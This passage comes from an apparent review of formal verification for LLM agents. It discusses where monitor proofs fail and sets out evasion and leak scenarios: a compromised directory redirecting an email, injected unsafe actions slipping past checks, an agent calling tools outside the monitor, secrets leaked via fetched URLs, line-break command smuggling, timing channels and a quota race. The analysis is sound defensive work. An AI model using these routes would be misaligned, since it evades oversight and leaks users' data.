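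The equivalence scores are rough. The judge was Sonnet 4.6, which two of the systems also use. Miranda and colleagues compared a different judge with human ratings and found a correlation of 0.61, or only 0.38 for rankings. An agent may also state a useful property that the reference lacks. The scores come from 176 test items, although the benchmark has 884 tasks. Gemini ran on a somewhat different set.

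*VERINA*, a benchmark of 189 Lean tasks, gives a milder result. The best model tested, OpenAI's o3, wrote correct code for 72.6% of tasks and sound, complete specifications for 52.3%. Newer models may do better on both benchmarks. *VeriEquivBench* uses a formally grounded score instead of comparing specifications with reference ones, which would remove the dependence on a judge's opinion.

Councilman and colleagues conclude that the user has to confirm the specification. Their system, Astrogator, checks programs in Ansible, a language for configuring remote computers. They give the example of a request to copy a file from /path/a to /path/b. Ansible runs on one computer, the controller, and manages others, so the request could mean copying within the remote computer, to it or from it. Councilman and colleagues meant the first, but all six models they tried wrote only programs that copy from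 the controller. Astrogator's formal queries make the choice visible in near-English:

```
move file from remote "/scratch/file.txt"
          to remote "/home/user/data.txt"
```

The queries also leave out technical details that a user couldn't confirm. A user can approve "install numpy" without knowing that Debian, a version of Linux, calls this package python3-numpy. Astrogator gets the name from a knowledge base that its designers compiled by hand, so the knowledge base is also part of the trusted base.

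In a test on 1,260 generated programs, Astrogator accepted 277 of the 334 correct ones and rejected 856 of the 926 incorrect ones. Of the 70 incorrect programs it accepted, 49 were for a single file-copying task, which had the ambiguity just described. Astrogator can list the choices in a program that the query doesn't specify, but in the test it accepted every program that satisfied the query. Councilman and colleagues wrote the queries themselves, so the test doesn't show whether users would notice a wrong one.

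Missing rules are harder to notice than wrong ones. In *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, a preprint from the company Ascendr, Koomullil (2026) tested an agent whose file operations had to satisfy preconditions checked in Lean. The checks blocked 67% of injected unsafe actions, compared with 28% for a list of forbidden patterns. The remaining third got through because the preconditions didn't cover them. Someone reading the log could see which conditions to add, but only after the attacks had succeeded.

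A short specification is easy to check for errors in what it contains. A reader who knows the task will probably notice if a one-page policy names the wrong Alice. But to notice that a rule is missing, the reader has to think of it independently, and a shorter policy doesn't make that easier.

### Tools that do not do what they declare

Suppose an attacker has taken over the company directory and replaced Alice's address with their own. Agenra's policy designates this directory as the source of the address. An agent that follows the user's instructions faithfully now produces this run:

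```
r = Read()             r is Confidential
c = Sanitize(r)        c is Public, with origin Sanitize
d = Lookup("Alice")    the slot now holds the attacker's address
a = Extract(d)         a is the attacker's address
Send(c, a)             allowed
```

The last call passes every check:

| Check | What the core finds | Result |
|---|---|---|
| label | c is Public | pass |
| origin | Sanitize produced c | pass |
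| recipient | a matches the address in the slot | pass |
| quota | both ledgers have one send left | pass |

Agenra's theorem about addresses still holds, because it guarantees only that the address in the slot came from a successful lookup in the designated directory, and this one did. It is an assumption that the directory lists the correct address for Alice.

The other rules still limit the damage. The attacker gets only the public fields, once, and the raw report stays blocked. But Alice gets nothing, because the email to the attacker used up the one allowed send.

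Shivakumar and colleagues show that the policy can safely allow a second lookup to recheck the address. This helps only if the attacker changes the entry between the two lookups, because the mismatch then blocks the email. If the attacker changed the entry before the first lookup, both lookups return the same address. Soteria checks each result against the tool's postcondition, but this wouldn't help either if the postcondition only required a well-formed address.

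A tool can also do more than its developer declared. Shivakumar and colleagues tested this by registering a batch tool with fewer effects than it performs, and Agenra allowed an undeclared deletion.

Descriptions of tools can be wrong even when no one has attacked the system. Councilman and colleagues had to describe Ansible's tools by hand, because the documentation was too informal and the code too complex to extract a description automatically. Their description identifies a file by its path. In practice, two paths can lead to the same file, so a program that changes the file at one path may also change what is at another path, which the verification assumes is unchanged.

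The best remedy for a compromised directory is a second source that the attacker doesn't control. For example, the application could require the address to carry a digital signature made with a key stored elsewhere. The attacker would then have to compromise both the directory and the key.

An auditor can see from Agenra's policy that the email's destination depends on one service, the directory, which is hard to learn from an ordinary agent's code. This is useful if the company runs the directory and can secure it. If an outside provider runs it, the company may be unable to inspect it, and an update could change its behaviour after the audit.

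### Unproved code around the proof

Verified software from before the current generation of agents provides the best evidence about connecting code. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three systems that keep copies of data on several servers. All three had machine-checked proofs, IronFleet's in Dafny and the others' in Coq. The researchers found 16 bugs:

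| Location | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| code between the proved part and the network or disk | 11 | a client could hide a second command inside a request |
| verification tools | 3 | a tool could report success for an incorrect program |
| specification | 2 | it did not guarantee that a request takes effect exactly once |

None of the bugs was in the proved protocols, although Fonseca and colleagues searched for protocol bugs for more than eight months. Mature systems without proofs had many such bugs.

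The hidden command worked because Verdi's connecting code treated a line break as the end of a request. A client could ask for a record whose name contained a line break followed by another request. The server carried out both, and later requests returned the wrong values. An agent's mail code could have a similar flaw if text after a line break in an approved field could add another recipient. The mail server would then deliver the message to someone the verified core had not checked.

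In Chapar, a server that received the same update twice applied it twice, because the proof assumed a network that never duplicates messages. Agenra's "at most one send" depends on a similar assumption, because Agenra counts calls to the mail tool. If a networking library inside the tool automatically retries a timed-out request, one counted call can produce two emails.

Tests of CompCert in 2011 had similar results. Researchers used Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs, to look for bugs in C compilers. They found bugs in unproved parts of CompCert that caused it to silently produce incorrect code, but in its proved middle stages they found none of the bugs they had found in every other compiler. According to their paper, as quoted in *A Clever Way to Find Compiler Bugs* (2019), they used about six years of processor time to test the development version of early 2011 and found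 no case of incorrect code.

Newer cases fit this pattern, including the bugs AWS found in Cedar's unproved parser. *Finding bugs in Raft implementations*, a post by Antithesis, which sells software testing, describes problems in implementations of Raft, the protocol behind Verdi's proof. Raft's formal specification describes the design, not the code that programmers write from it.

Assumptions inside a Lean proof can be checked automatically with the command `#print axioms`, which lists every axiom that a theorem depends on, including those that only its lemmas use. Koomullil accepts a proof only if Lean's kernel, the small program that checks proofs, accepts it and the list contains nothing beyond Lean's three standard axioms and assumptions that the author has declared by name.

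The second condition is necessary because a program could answer every request for a proof with `sorry`, and Lean would accept the file with a warning. Each `sorry` adds an axiom called `sorryAx`, which appears in the list. Of the 46 checked results in Koomullil's library, 17 use no axioms and 29 use only the standard and declared ones. Some declared assumptions concern judgements by models or people, such as whether two sentences mean the same thing. In Lean4Agent, the same command would show which theorems depend on LLMExec, the assumption that the model fulfils every contract.

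This kind of audit can't detect a theorem that is too weak. A theorem that states only "True" needs no axioms, so CompCert4Lean's empty theorems could have passed. The list of axioms also omits code that Lean's compiler substitutes for a proved function, as in LLMbda's network call, because the substitution changes the running program but not the proof.

The argument for a small trusted base is strongest for connecting code. The interface components at fault in Fonseca and colleagues' study typically had only a few hundred lines, in systems of 20,000 to 54,000 lines. The researchers' testing kit for the unproved parts detected 13 of the 16 bugs. But they studied only three research prototypes and left out bugs in the operating system, the verifier's core and the hardware, so their results don't show that those are safe. An agent's connecting code also grows with every tool, because each one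 needs its own adapter.

### Effects outside the modelled interface

Effect exclusivity, the assumption that every outside effect passes through the verified interface, is harder to audit because it covers the whole machine. Isolation has failed in practice. OpenAI reported that in July 2026 its agents broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, during a cybersecurity evaluation that was supposed to be isolated.

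The weak point may be in the same process as the monitor. Agenra's Python layer gives the agent objects that stand for stored values and relies on the agent not reaching anything else. Shivakumar and colleagues note that this doesn't isolate arbitrary Python code. An agent that could run its own Python there might call the mail tool directly, without a check by the Lean core.

A developer can also overlook an effect when a tool appears only to read data. A tool that fetches web pages, for example, also sends each address it requests to whoever runs the server. If an agent requests a page on an attacker's site and includes a secret in the address, the attacker receives the secret. A policy that treats the tool only as a source of data would miss this leak.

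One remedy is to reject anything the formal model can't describe, as Astrogator does with shell commands. Councilman and colleagues told the LLMs not to use shell commands, but 130 of the generated programs still did. Astrogator rejected all 130, including nine that were correct.

A developer can also keep passwords and access keys away from the agent. If only the monitor's process has the password for the mail server, an agent that gets around the monitor still can't log in. It would have to steal the password or find another way out.

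A short list of permitted tools helps an auditor find unlisted channels only if the operating system blocks every connection by default. The auditor can then compare the list with the connections that the system allows. The guarantee still depends on the operating system, which is usually large and has not been proved correct.

### False text and misled reviewers

If a language model writes Alice's summary, the summary can satisfy every rule about labels and recipients and still be false. Koomullil attempts only *computational verification*, which establishes that a stated calculation on the model's output is correct. He distinguishes this from *semantic verification*, which would establish that a text is true.

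One of his certificates concerns answers based on retrieved documents. A model splits the answer into separate claims, and a model judges whether the documents support or contradict each one. If wᵢ is the weight of claim i, with all weights adding up to 1, the system releases the answer only if

Σ wᵢ ≤ θ, summed over the contradicted and disputed claims,

where θ is a limit set in advance. Suppose a medical recommendation makes 20 equally weighted claims. The documents support 19 of them, but the drug's own label contradicts the claim that the drug is safe for this patient's kidneys. A score that counts only support would be a reassuring 95%. The contradicted share is 5%, so a limit of 2% blocks the answer.

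Lean proves that the gate blocks every answer over the limit. It doesn't prove that the models split the answer or judged the claims correctly. In a trial on HotpotQA, a question-answering benchmark, the gate caught every contradiction that Koomullil had inserted, with a false-block rate of 6.4%. A simpler test based on text similarity needed a false-block rate of 26.6% to catch them all. Koomullil had revised his hypotheses in earlier rounds of the trial, so the result needs independent replication. He acknowledges that the method can't catch a false claim if the model repeats it consistently and corrupted documents support it.

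A human reviewer might catch such a claim. A reviewer who knew Alice's address could also have stopped the email in the compromised directory example. Agenra's one-time approvals prevent the agent from showing the reviewer one email and sending another. Even if the agent computes an identical summary again, it needs a new approval.

The reviewer can still approve a bad email, and Agenra can't check whether an approval was sensible. An attacker could register an address that differs from Alice's by one similar-looking character. A reviewer may also rely on the agent's explanation of the email, and a hijacked model can write that explanation. Councilman and colleagues cite research showing that people often struggle to check code written by language models, which is one reason Astrogator's users confirm a query in near-English.

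The safest approach is to assume nothing about the reviewer, just as the proofs assume nothing about the model. When Shivakumar and colleagues search the report policy for mistakes, their simulated reviewer approves every email the agent proposes, so the other rules must stop any bad email on their own. This works for labels, origins and quotas, but it can't catch false statements, because no other rule checks for them.

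An explicit trusted base helps less with human judgement. A company can use it to identify which decisions depend on a reviewer, then plant errors and measure how often reviewers miss them. The list of assumptions alone can't establish the miss rate, which may also change as reviewers get tired or used to approving.

### Timing, endless runs and simultaneous calls

Neither LLMbda's noninterference theorem nor Agenra's confidentiality theorem covers timing. Suppose an agent always emails Alice the same public summary, but first performs a long calculation if a secret field shows that layoffs are planned. The email arrives after 12 seconds if layoffs are planned and after 4 seconds otherwise. If Alice knows how the agent works, she can infer the secret from the delay.

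If an observer can distinguish k arrival times, one run can reveal up to log₂ k bits through timing. A developer can reduce k by delaying the email. If emails go out only on the minute and at most eight minutes after the request, there are eight possible times, so the limit is 3 bits. If every email goes out after exactly eight minutes, timing reveals nothing, provided every run has finished by then.

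Whether a run finishes can also reveal a secret, but at most one bit per run, so a developer can reduce the leak by capping the number of runs. With three runs instead of ten, the attack on CaMeL's retry loop could only narrow the 1,024 possible balances down to 128. Under that cap, a harmless program also can't be retried after three failures.

Simultaneous calls cause a different problem, because they break the assumption in Agenra's proofs that calls come one at a time. Here is what could happen if a monitor handled two sends at once, with a quota of one:

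| Step | First send | Second send | Recorded quota |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | finds one use left | | 1 |
| 2 | | finds one use left | 1 |
| 3 | sets the quota to 0 and sends | | 0 |
| 4 | | sets the quota to 0 and sends | 0 |

Each send passes its check, but two emails go out. Agenra prevents this with a lock. No other call can start, and nobody can issue an approval, until the current call has finished and the core has processed its result.

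The lock covers only one instance of the monitor. If the company accidentally starts the task twice, each instance has its own ledgers and can send Alice an email. If the mail server never answers, the lock would presumably hold up every later call, unless the tool has a time limit.

An auditor can check a lock by reading a few lines of code, and a limit on the number of runs by reading a single setting. Timing is much harder to audit, because the length of a run depends on the compiler, the hardware and how busy the model's provider is. If the system sends every email at a fixed time, most of this no longer matters. The auditor then has to check only the code that holds the email back, including what that code does when a run isn't finished in time.
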